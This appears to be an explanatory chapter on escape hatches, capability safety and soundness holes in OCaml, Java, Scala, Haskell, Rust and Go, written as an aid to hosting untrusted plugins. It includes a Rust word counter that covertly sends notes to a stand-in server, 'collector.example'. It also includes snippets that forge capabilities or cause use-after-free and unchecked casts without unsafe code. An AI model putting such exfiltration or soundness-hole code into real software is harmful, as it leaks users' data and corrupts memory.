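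The cast is enough to forge a capability. Suppose an OCaml host defines a module `Notes` with a private type `t`, which is a folder's path stored as text. Other modules cannot see that `t` is text, and can get a `t` only from the host. A plugin can write:

```ocaml
let disk : Notes.t =
  Marshal.from_string (Marshal.to_string "/" []) 0
```

The compiler accepts `disk` as a folder that the host approved, and `Notes.read` will open any file on the disk. The plugin's author only needs to guess how the host represents a folder. In Java, by contrast, the rebuilt object belongs to the class that the program sees, even if its private fields hold invalid values.

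### What happens to a saved capability

A runtime can make references unforgeable because it controls how code obtains them. But anyone who holds a serialized object's bytes can copy or edit them. So if a program serializes an object that contains a capability, the designer of the serialization system has to decide what authority the rebuilt object should have.

The system can refuse to serialize an object, as `Marshal` does for open files. This is safe, but an application that has to restart then needs another way to restore its objects.

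The system can also save a description of the resource and use it to reopen the resource on reading. Java's `File` objects are serializable and contain little more than a path. If `FileSystem` worked the same way, the plugin could save its folder, change `/notes` to `/` in the saved data and read the object back. The rebuilt object would get its authority from the runtime, which can open any file the operating system allows.

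A plugin could use serialization to keep `fs` after the host's block of code has ended, even without editing the bytes. Scala's compiler rejects a result whose type still refers to `fs` at that point, but the type of a byte array contains no such reference. The plugin could serialize `fs` during the block, return the bytes as ordinary data and rebuild the capability the next day.

### Miller's scheme

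Mark Miller's *Safe Serialization Under Mutual Suspicion*, written for the capability language E, addresses the problem. In June 2003, when the paper had just gone out for comment, participants in *MaObjectSerializer documentation and usage*, a mailing-list thread about an object database, discussed it as a guide to a security model.

The paper's central idea came from the computer scientist Jonathan Rees, according to Christine Lemmer-Webber (2023), who based a later system called Aurie on the paper. A program creates an object by evaluating an expression, which usually means calling a function with some arguments. Serialization can reverse this by finding an expression that would create the object.

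For the notes plugin, the process goes like this:

1. The serializer asks the `NoteReader` object which call would recreate it. The answer is a call to the function `makeNoteReader` with the `FileSystem` object as its argument.
2. The serializer asks the same question about each object in the answer, and continues until it reaches simple data or an object on a list that the host has supplied. The list gives names to live objects. Here it contains `makeNoteReader` and the file system, under the name `notesFolder`.
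3. It writes the expression `makeNoteReader(notesFolder)`. Neither the folder's path nor any authority over it appears in the text.
4. To rebuild the object, the reader evaluates the expression with its own table of names and live objects.

The rebuilt object can have only the authority that the reader puts in the table. If the reader's `notesFolder` is a copy of the notes on another computer, the new `NoteReader` reads the copy. If the table has no `notesFolder`, the evaluation fails. An attacker who changes the text to `makeNoteReader(wholeDisk)` gains nothing unless the reader has put a `wholeDisk` in the table.

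The scheme also prevents the earlier attacks in this section. It rebuilds objects by calling ordinary functions, so a function that makes even counters can reject 7. Function names also come from the table, so the text cannot trigger arbitrary library code the way a gadget chain does.

An attacker can still misuse whatever the table contains. Suppose it has entries for both the notes and a folder of private letters, because the host saves objects that use each. Someone who edits the serialized text can swap the names, and a plugin meant to read notes will read letters. A careful host gives each plugin its own table, containing only what that plugin may have.

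The answer to the question in the first step also needs protection, because it contains the live `FileSystem` object. If `NoteReader` gave that answer to everyone, the plugin could get the object by making the same request. Capability languages can prevent this with a pair of functions called a *sealer* and an *unsealer*. The sealer puts a value in a box that only the matching unsealer can open. *The Heart of Spritely*, the Spritely Institute's paper on Goblins, uses such a pair for a blog. Goblins is the programming system for which Lemmer-Webber wrote Aurie. Each blog post carries a sealed reference to its editor, which only the blog's administrator object can open. `NoteReader` could likewise seal its answer so that only the host's serializer can read it.

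Java's built-in serialization requires almost no work from whoever writes a class, whereas Miller's scheme requires each object to be able to describe itself. Lemmer-Webber first wrote Aurie as a separate library, which showed that it needed no special language support. But many standard Goblins objects could not describe themselves, so programs that used them could not save their state. She then rewrote Aurie as part of Goblins. The order in which objects are restored can also cause failures. In E, an object's description could refer to a function belonging to another saved object, and the deserializer might try to call that function before the other object existed.

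The JavaScript package `marshal` applies the same principle to data that contains references. According to its description on Socket, a site that checks software packages, it returns a JSON body and a list of slots. For an object with no references, such as `{"a":1}`, the body is the object's ordinary JSON and the list is empty. If an object contains a live reference, the body has a marker and the list has an identifier. The calling program supplies one function that turns references into identifiers and another that turns identifiers back into references, so the second function determines what authority the reader gets.

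Miller's scheme also handles permissions that change after the program saves an object. Suppose the host withdraws the plugin's access to the notes on Tuesday, but the plugin has kept bytes from Monday. If those bytes contained the permission, as a path or a flag, rebuilding the object would restore the access. In Miller's scheme they contain the name `notesFolder` instead, and the host can withhold access by leaving that name out of Tuesday's table.

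## Unsafe Rust

Rust requires code that could corrupt memory to sit inside a block labelled `unsafe`. Everything outside those blocks is *safe Rust*, which the language guarantees against memory errors as long as the `unsafe` code is correct. Reviewers can therefore concentrate on those blocks. But the guarantee covers only memory, and confining a plugin also requires a guarantee about effects, which Rust does not offer.

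### What an unsafe block permits

Safe Rust prevents memory errors mainly through rules about references. Each value normally has one owner, and other code can borrow it through a reference. At any moment a value may have either one reference that can change it or any number that can only read it. The compiler's *borrow checker* enforces this and also rejects references that could outlive the value.

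Rust's *Unsafety*, a page of the language's reference manual, lists the operations that safe code may not perform. The main ones are:

- following a *raw pointer*, which is a memory address that the borrow checker does not track
- calling a function marked `unsafe`, which includes most foreign functions
- reading or writing a global variable that other threads may be changing
- reading a field of a union, a type that stores different kinds of value in the same memory
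- implementing an unsafe trait, which is an interface whose implementers promise something the compiler cannot check

One of the unsafe functions, `transmute`, converts a value to another type without checking that the conversion makes sense, like Haskell's `unsafeCoerce`.

An `unsafe` block leaves Rust's other checks on. Types still have to match, `text[i]` still checks that `i` is within bounds, and, as Brown University's *Unsafe Rust* stresses, the borrow checker still checks ordinary references. In an earlier interview study that McCormack and colleagues describe, 10 of 26 developers who had written unsafe code wrongly believed `unsafe` switched off Rust's static safety rules entirely.

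### A sound wrapper and an unsound one

Reading outside an array is an example of *undefined behaviour*, an error after which the language places no limits on what the program does. The compiler assumes that undefined behaviour never happens and optimises accordingly, so the damage can appear far from the mistake.

Whoever wraps unsafe code in a safe function takes on this obligation:

> No program written in safe Rust may be able to cause undefined behaviour by calling the function, whatever arguments it passes.

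A function that meets the obligation is *sound*. Suppose the word counter reads single bytes of a note through a raw pointer:

```rust
pub fn byte_at(text: &[u8], i: usize) -> Option<u8> {
    if i < text.len() {
        Some(unsafe { *text.as_ptr().add(i) })
    } else {
        None
    }
}
```

Here `text` is a *slice*, a reference to a run of bytes together with its length. If `i` is smaller than the length, the function calculates the address of byte `i` and reads it. A caller who asks for byte 5,000 of a four-byte note gets `None`.

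This version leaves out the check:

```rust
pub fn byte_at(text: &[u8], i: usize) -> u8 {
    unsafe { *text.as_ptr().add(i) }
}
```

The compiler accepts it too. Now `byte_at(b"milk", 5000)` may crash, or it may return a byte of someone else's note or of a password. The call needs no `unsafe` block, so a plugin written in safe Rust can make it. By Rust's convention, the author of `byte_at` is at fault, even if the caller passes an absurd index. The author could also have declared the function `unsafe` and documented that `i` must be within bounds. Callers would then need their own `unsafe` block and would share the responsibility.

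The error can also be outside the `unsafe` block. Suppose a type holds a pointer to some bytes and stores the number of bytes in a private field. Its read function checks the index `i` against that field before following the pointer. If a safe method in the same module sets the field too high, the read can go out of bounds even though the `unsafe` code hasn't changed. A reviewer therefore has to read every function that can change the field, but because the field is private, those functions are all in one module.

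### How RustBelt proves a library sound

Testing `byte_at` cannot cover all its callers, and the standard type soundness theorem does not apply to programs that contain unsafe code. Many of Rust's standard types depend on such code. The lock type `Mutex`, for example, uses it to let several threads take turns changing one value through references that normally permit only reading.

*RustBelt* (Jung, Jourdan and colleagues, 2018) solved this for a model language called λRust. It defines the meaning of each type, independently of how the code inside is written, as a statement in Iris, a logic for reasoning about which part of a program owns which memory. For the type of the first `byte_at`, the statement would require that for every slice and every number, the function runs without an invalid memory access and returns a valid `Option<u8>`. The version with the check satisfies this, while the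 version without it fails a similar condition for its own type as soon as `i` equals the length.

The proof has three parts:

1. Every typing rule of λRust is true of these meanings, so code that passes the type checker automatically satisfies the meaning of its type.
2. A complete program that satisfies the meaning of its type never makes an invalid memory access and never has a *data race*, in which threads access the same memory without coordination and at least one of them writes.
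3. Each library that uses unsafe code satisfies the meaning of its public interface.

Jung and colleagues proved the first two parts once and for all, so anyone who writes a new unsafe library has to prove only the third. They proved it for versions of several standard libraries, including `Arc`, `Rc`, `Cell`, `RefCell`, `Mutex` and `RwLock`, and checked all the proofs in Coq.

The proof for `Mutex` gives each type two meanings, one for owning a value and one for holding a shared reference to it. For a shared mutex, the second meaning describes a flag in memory. When the flag is true, the thread that took the lock has the right to access the contents, and when it is false, that right is stored with the lock. A thread takes the lock by atomically changing the flag from false to true and receives the right in the same step, so two threads can never have it at once.

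Proofs about separate libraries can be combined because they all use the same meanings for types. This matters in Rust, where one well-known bug arose from combining several libraries that each seemed safe alone. An earlier tool, CRUST, tested one library at a time, so it could not find such bugs.

The work also exposed an error in Rust's standard library involving `MutexGuard`, the object that a thread holds while it has the lock. Rust let threads share some guards whose contents were not safe to share, so safe code could cause a data race. The compiler had inferred that sharing was allowed and the library had not overridden this, so the error did not come from a wrong line in an `unsafe` block.

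RustBelt's guarantee is narrower than its list of libraries suggests. Jung and colleagues verified translations into λRust, and their mutex used a simple lock they wrote themselves, whereas the real one called the operating system. λRust leaves out the weaker memory operations that `Arc` uses for speed, as well as trait objects, the automatic clean-up of values and the unwinding that follows a *panic* (Rust's term for a program error that stops a thread). It also has no slices, so it could not express `byte_at` exactly. The theorem covers only memory and thread safety, so a sorting function that returned its input unsorted would satisfy it.

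Proofs of this kind take experts a long time, and researchers have tried to reduce the work. *A Hybrid Approach to Semi-automated Rust Verification* (2024) connects Creusot, an automatic tool for safe code, with Gillian-Rust, a semi-automatic tool for unsafe code. In *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification*, Kan, Kan and Ertel (2026) asked a general coding agent running Claude Opus 4.7 to prove the 217 lemmas about Rust's libraries that come with RustBelt. The agent wrote a proof, Coq checked it, and the agent revised it after each failure, up to thirty times. It proved all 217 without human help.

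Coq checks the proofs, so they are reliable. But people had already stated the lemmas and defined what each type means, and the model may have seen the original proofs, which are public, in training. The experiment does not show that an agent could work out the right condition for a new library.

### Why developers use unsafe code

Few Rust programmers prove anything about their unsafe code. Only 10 of the 160 developers in the survey by McCormack and colleagues had used tools based on formal methods.

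A 2023 survey asked Rust developers why they had used unsafe code and let them choose several answers. Of those who answered, 77% knew of no safe alternative, 47% wanted better speed or memory use, and 18% found unsafe code easier. Much of the first group needed unsafe code to call foreign functions, since 70% of all respondents called them. Others were writing operating systems or just-in-time compilers, which have to jump to addresses that no type checker can verify.

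Programmers who used unsafe code for speed were often guessing that it helped. Only 46% of them measured the difference at least most of the time. One interviewee didn't check that text from Python was valid, reasoning that Python would only supply valid text. This is like dropping the bounds check from `byte_at` because no caller would pass a large number. Another interviewee found a font library's interface too restrictive and used `transmute` to make the compiler treat some objects as lasting for the whole program.

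Most respondents (88%) had published a safe interface around unsafe code. Many interviewees who had done this could not say whether their interfaces were sound in every situation. One said that library authors do their best, "but god knows if there's a hole in it".

Part of the doubt about unsafe code comes from Rust itself, which has no complete specification of what such code may do. One interviewee described writing it "against the void". Researchers have proposed two sets of rules for how raw pointers and references may overlap, Stacked Borrows and Tree Borrows, but neither is official. If a program uses a reference to a structure's first field to reach the next field, Stacked Borrows treats this as undefined behaviour, while Tree Borrows allows it.

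In the survey, 88% of respondents checked their dependencies' unsafe code only sometimes or never. Miri's slowness, poor support for foreign calls, and other gaps had put off 62% of those who had tried it. One team working on a just-in-time compiler had dismissed Miri as useless for their program. After someone found a vulnerability, they ran Miri on the tests that made no foreign calls and learned that it would have caught the flaw.

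The participants were experienced volunteers, with about four years of Rust on average, and McCormack and colleagues regard their answers as a best case. The study recorded what developers believed about their code but did not test whether they were right.

### Defects in practice

Google's Android figures suggest that careful teams do much better than these doubts imply. Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that the platform has about 5 million lines of Rust and has had one potential memory-safety vulnerability in that code, which Google fixed before any public release. That is 0.2 per million lines, compared with roughly 1,000 per million for Android's C and C++ code.

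The flaw was a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, an image-reading library. According to The Hacker News (2025), it could have let an attacker run code remotely. Android's memory allocator, Scudo, places inaccessible regions around large blocks of memory, so the overflow caused a crash instead of silently overwriting other data.

About 4% of Android's Rust code, some 200,000 lines, is in `unsafe` blocks. Those lines would contain about 200 vulnerabilities if they had the same vulnerability rate as C code. Vander Stoep suggests three reasons why they contain fewer: most of Rust's checks still apply inside the blocks, encapsulation lets programmers reason about a small area of code, and reviewers examine code marked `unsafe` more closely.

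A rate based on one event is imprecise, but chance alone does not explain a gap this large. Even if the true count were five or six, the rate would be only about one per million lines. The comparison has other weaknesses. It counts only known flaws, and people have had many more years to search the C and C++ code. When Google (2022) gave a similar density for that code, its examples were media, Bluetooth and NFC, which process data from outside the phone and attract attackers. Android's developers also work under stricter review than most authors of public packages.

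McCormack and colleagues describe an experiment in which a version of Miri extended to follow calls into foreign code found 46 bugs in 37 public packages, one of them maintained by the Rust project. In their own survey, 35% of respondents who had called foreign functions had encountered declarations that did not match the foreign code.

These figures measure accidental defects, so they help developers of a host program judge a well-reviewed library but not a stranger's plugin, which may be malicious. The developers would want to forbid `unsafe` in the plugin whatever the average defect rate.

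### Safe Rust can open any file

Forbidding `unsafe` is easy. The first line of this word counter makes the compiler reject any `unsafe` block in the package:

```rust
#![forbid(unsafe_code)]

use std::io::Write;
use std::net::TcpStream;

pub fn count_words(text: &str) -> usize {
    if let Ok(mut server) = TcpStream::connect("collector.example:80") {
        let _ = server.write_all(text.as_bytes());
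    }
    text.split_whitespace().count()
}
```

A Rust function that counts the words in a set of notes can send every note to a stranger's server before returning the count, and it will still compile. In Haskell, the author would need `unsafePerformIO` to give such a function a pure type. In Rust, the author needs no escape hatch because Rust's types do not record effects.

Rust's definition of safety allows safe code to open files and network connections. `TcpStream::connect` relies on an unsafe call to the operating system inside the standard library, but safe callers cannot use the function to corrupt memory. The definition does not cover whether the connection should be opened, so the list of unsafe operations includes neither `std::net` nor the file functions in `std::fs`.

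A ban on `unsafe` is still worth having because it stops the plugin's own code from making foreign calls or overwriting the host's memory. It does not fully protect memory, since it covers the plugin's package but not its dependencies, and safe Rust has soundness holes of its own. Even a perfect ban would leave the plugin with access to every file and connection that the operating system allows the host.

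### Capabilities by convention

The library cap-std offers versions of Rust's file and network functions that work only through objects passed to the code. With it, the word counter can ask for a folder:

```rust
pub fn count_words(notes: &Dir, name: &str) -> io::Result<usize> {
    let text = notes.read_to_string(name)?;
    Ok(text.split_whitespace().count())
}
```

A `Dir` represents an open directory, and its methods fail on any path that leads outside it. Examples are `../letters/anna.txt`, an absolute path such as `/etc/passwd`, and a symbolic link (a file that redirects to another path) that points outside the directory. A similar type, `Pool`, holds a set of network addresses and allows connections only to those.

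`Dir` does the same check as `inNotesFolder`, the hand-written path check in the first section, but it also handles a case that a simple check misses, where another program replaces a folder with a symbolic link after the check and before the file opens. Recent versions of Linux have a system call, `openat2`, that checks the path and opens the file in one operation. On other systems, cap-std opens the path one part at a time. For `red/green/blue`, that takes five calls, three to open the parts and two to close the folders it has passed through.

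*Introducing cap-std, a capability-based version of the Rust standard library* (sunfishcode) describes the library's purpose as protecting honest code against malicious input. A web server that joins a folder name to a path supplied by a visitor may serve files from anywhere on the disk. Using cap-std's `Dir` prevents this mistake. A `&Dir` parameter also shows readers which files a function is meant to use.

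Nothing obliges the function to keep to them. The plugin's author can add this line to `count_words` without changing its type:

```rust
let letter = std::fs::read_to_string("/home/me/letters/anna.txt");
```

The cap-std documentation warns that the library is "not a sandbox for untrusted Rust code", which can bypass it with `unsafe` or the ordinary functions in `std::fs`. With `unsafe`, a plugin can call C's `open` directly or overwrite the file descriptor that identifies a `Dir`'s directory to the operating system. It can also open files through `std::fs` without any `unsafe` code.

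A change in cap-std's design illustrates how Rust separates memory safety from authority. A program can get its first `Dir` by calling `Dir::open_ambient_dir` with a plain path. In version 0.1.0 that function was `unsafe`, although it could not corrupt memory. Later versions made it safe and added an argument of type `AmbientAuthority`. Any code, including a plugin, can obtain that argument by calling `ambient_authority()`. The call only marks, for people searching the code, that the caller has chosen to use ambient authority.

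A host can search for such calls with Clippy, Rust's tool for detecting questionable code, and could also use it to reject `std::fs`. The host would also have to scan the plugin's dependencies and stop the plugin from turning off the warnings in its own source.

A stronger option is to compile the plugin to WebAssembly, an instruction format designed to run in a sandbox. WASI, the interface through which WebAssembly programs reach the operating system, applies the same rule as `Dir` to every file access, and the WebAssembly runtime Wasmtime uses cap-std to implement it. The plugin can still call `std::fs`, but it can reach only the directories the host has given it, and its `unsafe` blocks can damage only its own memory.

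## How many escape hatches languages have

The number of escape hatches in Rust depends on what is counted. All memory-unsafe operations require one keyword, `unsafe`. There are about six such operations, and more than 24,000 published packages use the keyword. These counts exclude compiler bugs that let a program corrupt memory without `unsafe`.

Developers of a program that hosts plugins need separate counts of the kinds of escape hatch, the soundness holes, and the libraries that use hatches. The compiler has to reject each kind of hatch, but soundness holes remain even after it rejects every declared one. The number of libraries that use hatches affects how much code the host has to trust when the plugin itself uses none. A single total would rank Haskell among the worst languages because it has many kinds of hatch, even though GHC has a mode that rejects them.

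### Kinds of escape hatch

The table lists the main declared hatches in six languages. The Go rows mostly follow the categories in Capslock, a Google tool that reports what a Go package can do.

| Language | Escape hatch | What it voids | Source of the list |
|---|---|---|---|
| Haskell | `unsafePerformIO` and its relatives | Purity | GHC's user guide, Terei and colleagues |
| | `unsafeCoerce` | Type safety, and through it purity and encapsulation | |
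| | Foreign imports with pure types | Purity | |
| | Template Haskell | Encapsulation | |
| | Generalised Newtype Deriving, `DerivingVia`, `Data.Coerce` | Encapsulation | |
| | Rewrite rules | Modular reasoning | |
| Java | Deep reflection | Encapsulation | Pressler and colleagues |
| | `sun.misc.Unsafe` | Encapsulation, type safety, memory safety | |
| | Native code | The same | |
| | Java agents | Encapsulation, by replacing methods | |
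| | Built-in serialization | The checks in constructors | SEI |
| Scala | Unchecked casts | Capability safety, local purity | Odersky and colleagues |
| | `unsafeAssumePure` | Capability safety, local purity | Scala's library |
| | Reflection and Java's other hatches | As for Java, and capability safety | Odersky and colleagues |
| Rust | Following raw pointers | Memory safety | McCormack and colleagues |
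| | Calling unsafe functions, including foreign ones | Memory safety, type safety | |
| | Changing global variables | Thread safety | |
| | Implementing unsafe traits | Memory and thread safety | |
| | Inline assembly | Memory safety | |
| | Reading union fields | Type safety | Rust's reference manual |
| OCaml | `Obj.magic` | Type safety, encapsulation | OCaml's manual |
| | `external` declarations | Type safety, memory safety | |
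| | `Marshal` | Type safety, encapsulation | |
| | Functions such as `Bytes.unsafe_to_string` | The rule that strings never change | |
| Go | `unsafe.Pointer` | Type safety, memory safety, encapsulation | Barney and Neto, Capslock |
| | C code, through a tool called cgo | Memory safety, encapsulation | Capslock |
| | Assembly code | Memory safety, encapsulation | |
| | The `go:linkname` directive | Encapsulation, by reaching private functions | |

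The number of rows is a poor measure of how dangerous a language is. One row for Scala covers all of Java's hatches. A single ban blocks all six of Rust's operations, while blocking Haskell's takes several. OCaml has fewer rows than Haskell, but a plugin can forge a value of any private type with `Obj.magic` alone.

The table also leaves out ambient authority, which code can use without an escape hatch. Of the six languages, only Haskell shows in a function's type that the function may open a file.

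Barney and Neto rank languages by *unsafe impedance*, the difficulty of writing and using unsafe code. They rate C# "none", Go and Java "low", Rust and Swift near the top of "low", and Python "high", because a Python programmer has to compile unsafe code with separate tools. They give no scoring rules and consider only memory errors, so Java's rating ignores reflection. Their rating for Go depends partly on a claim that following a nil pointer (one that points to nothing) is undefined behaviour, as in C, but in Go it stops the program with a run-time error. These problems make the ranking a poor basis for a host's choice of language.

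### A lifetime hole in Rust

A reference in Rust has a *lifetime*, the part of the program during which code may use it. Lifetimes can be named, as in `&'a T`, a reference to a `T` that is valid for `'a`. The lifetime `'static` lasts until the program ends. The borrow checker normally stops code from extending a reference's lifetime, because the value it refers to might no longer exist.

A bug report from 28 May 2015, number 25860 in Rust's issue tracker, contains a short program that extends one. With the names changed, it looks like this:

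```rust
static PROOF: &'static &'static () = &&();

fn relabel<'a, 'b, T>(_: &'a &'b (), value: &'b T) -> &'a T {
    value
}

fn keep_forever<'n, T>(value: &'n T) -> &'static T {
    let f: fn(&'static &'n (), &'n T) -> &'static T = relabel;
    f(PROOF, value)
}
```

The function `relabel` receives a reference valid for `'b` and returns it as valid for `'a`. That is safe only if `'b` lasts at least as long as `'a`, which Rust writes as `'b: 'a`. The compiler infers this condition, called an *implied bound*, from the type of the first argument, which is a reference valid for `'a` to another reference valid for `'b`. The outer reference should never outlive the inner one, so the compiler assumes `'b: 'a` inside `relabel` and accepts the function.

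The next function chooses `'static` for `'a` and the short lifetime `'n` for `'b`. The implied bound is now `'n: 'static`, which is false for most references. The compiler should reject the line that defines `f`, but the type of `relabel` does not include the bound, and the compiler did not check it on that line.

The call still needs a first argument of type `&'static &'n ()`. Rust lets code use a long-lived reference where a shorter-lived one would do, which is harmless in itself. `PROOF` contains two permanent references, so Rust also accepts it as the type with a shorter inner lifetime. The condition holds for `PROOF` as defined but not for the lifetimes in the call. The function returns `value` with a permanent lifetime.

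A program can then read memory that it has already released:

```rust
let stale: &'static String = {
    let note = String::from("milk");
    keep_forever(&note)
};
println!("{}", stale);
```

Rust frees `note` at the closing brace, and the last line reads whatever now occupies its memory. This code contains no `unsafe`.

The package cve-rs uses the same hole to build several well-known kinds of vulnerability. Its unchecked cast starts with a value that can hold either an `A` or a `B`. The code takes a reference to the `B` part, extends the reference's lifetime, stores an `A` in the same place and reads it through the old reference. RustSec's *cve-rs introduces memory vulnerabilities in safe Rust* (2025), an entry in Rust's security advisory database, calls the package a joke that nobody should use. It lists no patched version because the fault is in the compiler.

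The current compiler rejects a simple form of the program, and the Rust Project keeps a test that checks for the error. But the new check does not cover function pointers that have to work for every lifetime, such as `for<'x> fn(_, &'x T) -> &'static T`, so the underlying hole is still open after eleven years.

A contributor to the forum thread *Soundness Concern* explains that the planned repair would make the compiler write the hidden condition into the function's type. The type of `relabel` would become `for<'a, 'b: 'a> fn(&'a &'b (), &'b T) -> &'a T`. Choosing `'static` for `'a` would then visibly require a permanent `'b`, and the compiler could reject violations. Rust cannot yet express a condition in that position, and adding it depends on a rewrite of the *trait solver*, the part of the compiler that works out which types satisfy which interfaces. The Rust Project's *Unblocking dormant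 traits* aims to have the new solver in the stable compiler by the end of 2026, but its *Project Zero*, a plan to fix every known soundness hole in the type system, dates the repair only as "Future". A quicker fix would also reject a good deal of valid code.

This hole poses little risk to programmers who aren't trying to exploit it. The person who opened the forum thread was choosing a language for a long-lived project, and some colleagues saw the bug as a reason to prefer C++. Nearly everyone who replied thought this was a poor reason. The bug requires references to references, an implied bound and a conversion to a function pointer, all in one place, and nobody had reported hitting it by accident. One participant pointed out that the lack of reports is weak evidence, because if there were a reliable way to detect affected code, the compiler would already include it.

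Another participant distinguished this from the case of someone who runs hostile code and relies on the absence of `unsafe` to make it harmless. Soundness holes matter in that case, although a plugin in ordinary Rust gains little from cve-rs that it could not get from the standard library. The hole cve-rs exploits would matter much more in a version of Rust without the file, network and process functions, because overwriting the host's memory might then be the plugin's only way to gain that access.

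### Holes in Java, Scala and Haskell

*Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* (Nada Amin and Ross Tate, 2016) presents a Java method that converts a value of any type to any other type without a cast. The method depends on `null`, which stands for "no object" and belongs to every class.

Their method uses a class declared as `Constrain<A, B extends A>`, whose second type must be a subtype of the first. It declares a variable of type `Constrain<U, ? super T>`, where the question mark stands for some unknown supertype of `T`. The class declaration requires this unknown type to be a subtype of `U` as well, so the compiler accepts a `T` as a `U`.

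The reasoning would be valid if the variable held an actual `Constrain` object, because nobody could create one for unrelated types. But the variable holds `null`, so the program never has to create such an object. Scala allows a similar argument with types that belong to an object. In Rust's case too, the compiler treats a value as evidence that a condition holds, and a program can supply a value of the right type even though the condition is false.

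In Java, run-time checks limit the damage. When a program converts the number 0 to a `String` this way, the runtime throws an exception because the object is an `Integer`. These checks use the classes of objects, but Scala's capability annotations exist only at compile time. A function that holds a network connection and a pure function can belong to the same class, so no run-time check would fail if a hole in the type system relabelled one as the other.

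Haskell does not check types at run time either. GHC's *Type families + hs-boot files = unsafeCoerce*, issue 9562, builds the unchecked cast from several modules that look innocent when GHC compiles them separately. It uses a *type family*, which is a function from types to types whose equations can be spread over different modules. The important parts, with new names for the functions, are:

```haskell
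-- module A
type family F a b

-- module B
type instance F a b = b
pick :: F a b -> a -> b
pick = const

-- module D
type instance F a b = a
cast :: a -> b
cast x = pick x x
```

In module B, `F a b` means `b`, so `pick` has type `b -> a -> b`. Defining it as the library function `const`, which returns its first argument, is therefore correct. In module D, `F a b` means `a`, so `pick` seems to have type `a -> a -> b`, and `pick x x` returns `x` as any type the caller chooses.

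GHC rejects two contradictory equations when it sees both. But D gets `pick` through an `hs-boot` file, a short module summary that GHC uses for circular imports. The summary gives the type of `pick` but omits B's equation for `F`. GHC detected the conflict when the reporter loaded all the modules into its interactive mode. Separate compilation produced a program that read `True` as a whole number and printed 2882303761534249061.

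The program still compiled when its main module was declared `Safe`, so the reporter, goldfire, raised the issue's priority. Goldfire proposed that `hs-boot` files list all the type equations of their modules, but called this solution terrible. Eisenberg cited this bug in April 2021 when he asked whether anyone relied on Safe Haskell. A host can block this route by refusing `hs-boot` files in plugins and in the packages they import.

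GHC's developers have closed other holes. GHC's *Type unsoundness with type families and UndecidableInstances* records one in version 7.6, with these two equations:

```haskell
type instance F (a -> a)      = Int
type instance F (a -> a -> a) = IO String
```

The two equations look compatible because no finite type matches both patterns. But GHC let programmers define an infinite type `LA` that equals `LA -> LA`. Replacing the second `LA` by its definition gives `LA -> LA -> LA`, so `LA` fits both equations, and `F LA` is both a number and an `IO` computation. The resulting program crashed. *generalized newtype and type families is unsound*, a GHC report on a release candidate of version 7.6.1, showed that combining type families with Generalised Newtype Deriving also yielded `unsafeCoerce`. It suggested that GHC treat every module using that extension as unsafe, as Safe Haskell still does.

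| Hole | What a program can do | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Rust, issue 25860 | Use a reference after its value is gone | Open; the compiler rejects the simplest form |
| Java and Scala, `null` as evidence | Relabel any value; Java's runtime detects wrong classes | Unfixed when Amin and Tate published in 2016 |
| GHC, issue 9562 | Relabel any value | Unfixed in April 2021 |
| GHC 7.6, infinite types | Treat a number as an `IO` computation | Fixed |

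### Why nobody has a total for soundness holes

Bug trackers list only the known soundness holes and mix them with other faults. The Rust compiler team's *2025 Q3 T-compiler P-high Issue Review* (2025), a July snapshot of high-priority bugs, contains at least 27 issues labelled unsound. Only a handful are errors in the type system. One lets a program bypass the rule that a type has a single implementation of each interface, and another involves `Pin`, a type meant to guarantee that a value will not move in memory.

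Most of the others are mistakes in generating machine code. On some ARM processors a rounding function gives wrong results, and in one case two equal pointers compare as different. Many affect only a particular processor or operating system. A hostile author could exploit some of them, but a perfect type checker would not prevent any of them. The list also omits issue 25860, which has only medium priority.

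*Well-Typed Programs Can Go Wrong* (Chaliasos et al., 2021) examined a random sample of 320 typing bugs in the compilers for Java, Scala, Kotlin and Groovy, which all run on the Java runtime. In more than half, the compiler wrongly rejected a correct program. Such bugs don't let unsafe programs through, so the number of typing bugs greatly overstates the number of soundness holes. Generics, which are types that take other types as parameters, were the most common language feature in the programs that exposed the bugs. Amin and Tate's method also uses generics.

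The sample shows that mistakes keep turning up in type checkers for large languages, and that some of them let incorrect programs through. A host that relies on a type checker should expect more holes and install compiler updates promptly. The sample does not give the number of holes in any of the four languages.

### Escape hatches in Rust packages

*Is Rust Used Safely by Software Developers?* (Evans, Campbell and Soffa, 2020) found that fewer than a third of packages in Rust's public registry used `unsafe` directly, but more than half had it in their own code or a dependency. About 38% had it only in a dependency, and only 27% had none in either place.

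Vytautas Astrauskas and colleagues (2020), in *How Do Programmers Use Unsafe Rust?*, analysed about 32,000 Rust packages from January 2020 and found unsafe code in about 24% of them. They tested whether programmers follow the community's advice to use little unsafe code, keep it easy to review and hide it behind safe interfaces. Most of the unsafe code was simple and well hidden, but programmers used more of it than the advice recommends, especially to call code in other languages.

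The most recent large count, from May 2024, is in the Rust Foundation's *Unsafe Rust in the Wild*. It reports about 145,000 packages, of which about 127,000 contained a significant amount of code. Of those 127,000, 24,362 (19.11%) used the `unsafe` keyword, and 34.35% directly called a package that used it. Such a call may not reach any unsafe code, since the package may use `unsafe` only in some other function.

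The share fell from 24% to 19% between the last two counts, but the two counts used different methods to select packages, so the drop may not reflect any change in habits. The number of packages rose from roughly 7,500 to more than 24,000 as the registry grew.

The studies also disagree about what the unsafe code does. According to the Rust Foundation, most uses are calls to code in other languages, usually C or C++. Evans and colleagues found that 65% of calls to unsafe functions went to functions written in Rust and 22.5% to C functions. The Rust Foundation gives no percentage, and its leading package, `windows`, contains a huge number of calls to Microsoft's operating system. A few packages like that can change the result if a study counts individual uses instead of packages. The difference matters because a reviewer can check a Rust function by reading more Rust, but checking a C function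 requires the source code and someone who knows C.

Counting packages doesn't show how much unsafe code each one has, so a package with one unsafe block counts the same as `windows`, which has many. The 4% of lines reported for Android in the previous section better indicates how much code a reviewer has to read, but it describes only one company's code.

### Java and Go

The large Java surveys predate the restrictions that Java's developers have introduced since version 9, so they describe an earlier period.

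*Use at Your Own Risk* (Mastrangelo et al., 2015) searched 86,479 compiled Java archives for uses of `sun.misc.Unsafe` and found that a quarter used it or depended on other code that did. The paper identified 14 patterns of use, which helps explain why Java's developers have taken so long to replace the class.

*Challenges for Static Analysis of Java Reflection* (Landman et al., 2017) examines 461 open-source Java projects and concludes that an analysis tool could not ignore reflection in 78% of them. This is much higher than the figure for `Unsafe`, but most reflection respects access rules. A program that looks up a public class by name breaks no encapsulation, although a tool may be unable to determine which class it will load. The 78% therefore measures how often reflection obstructs a reviewer, and is little evidence of how often programs open private fields.

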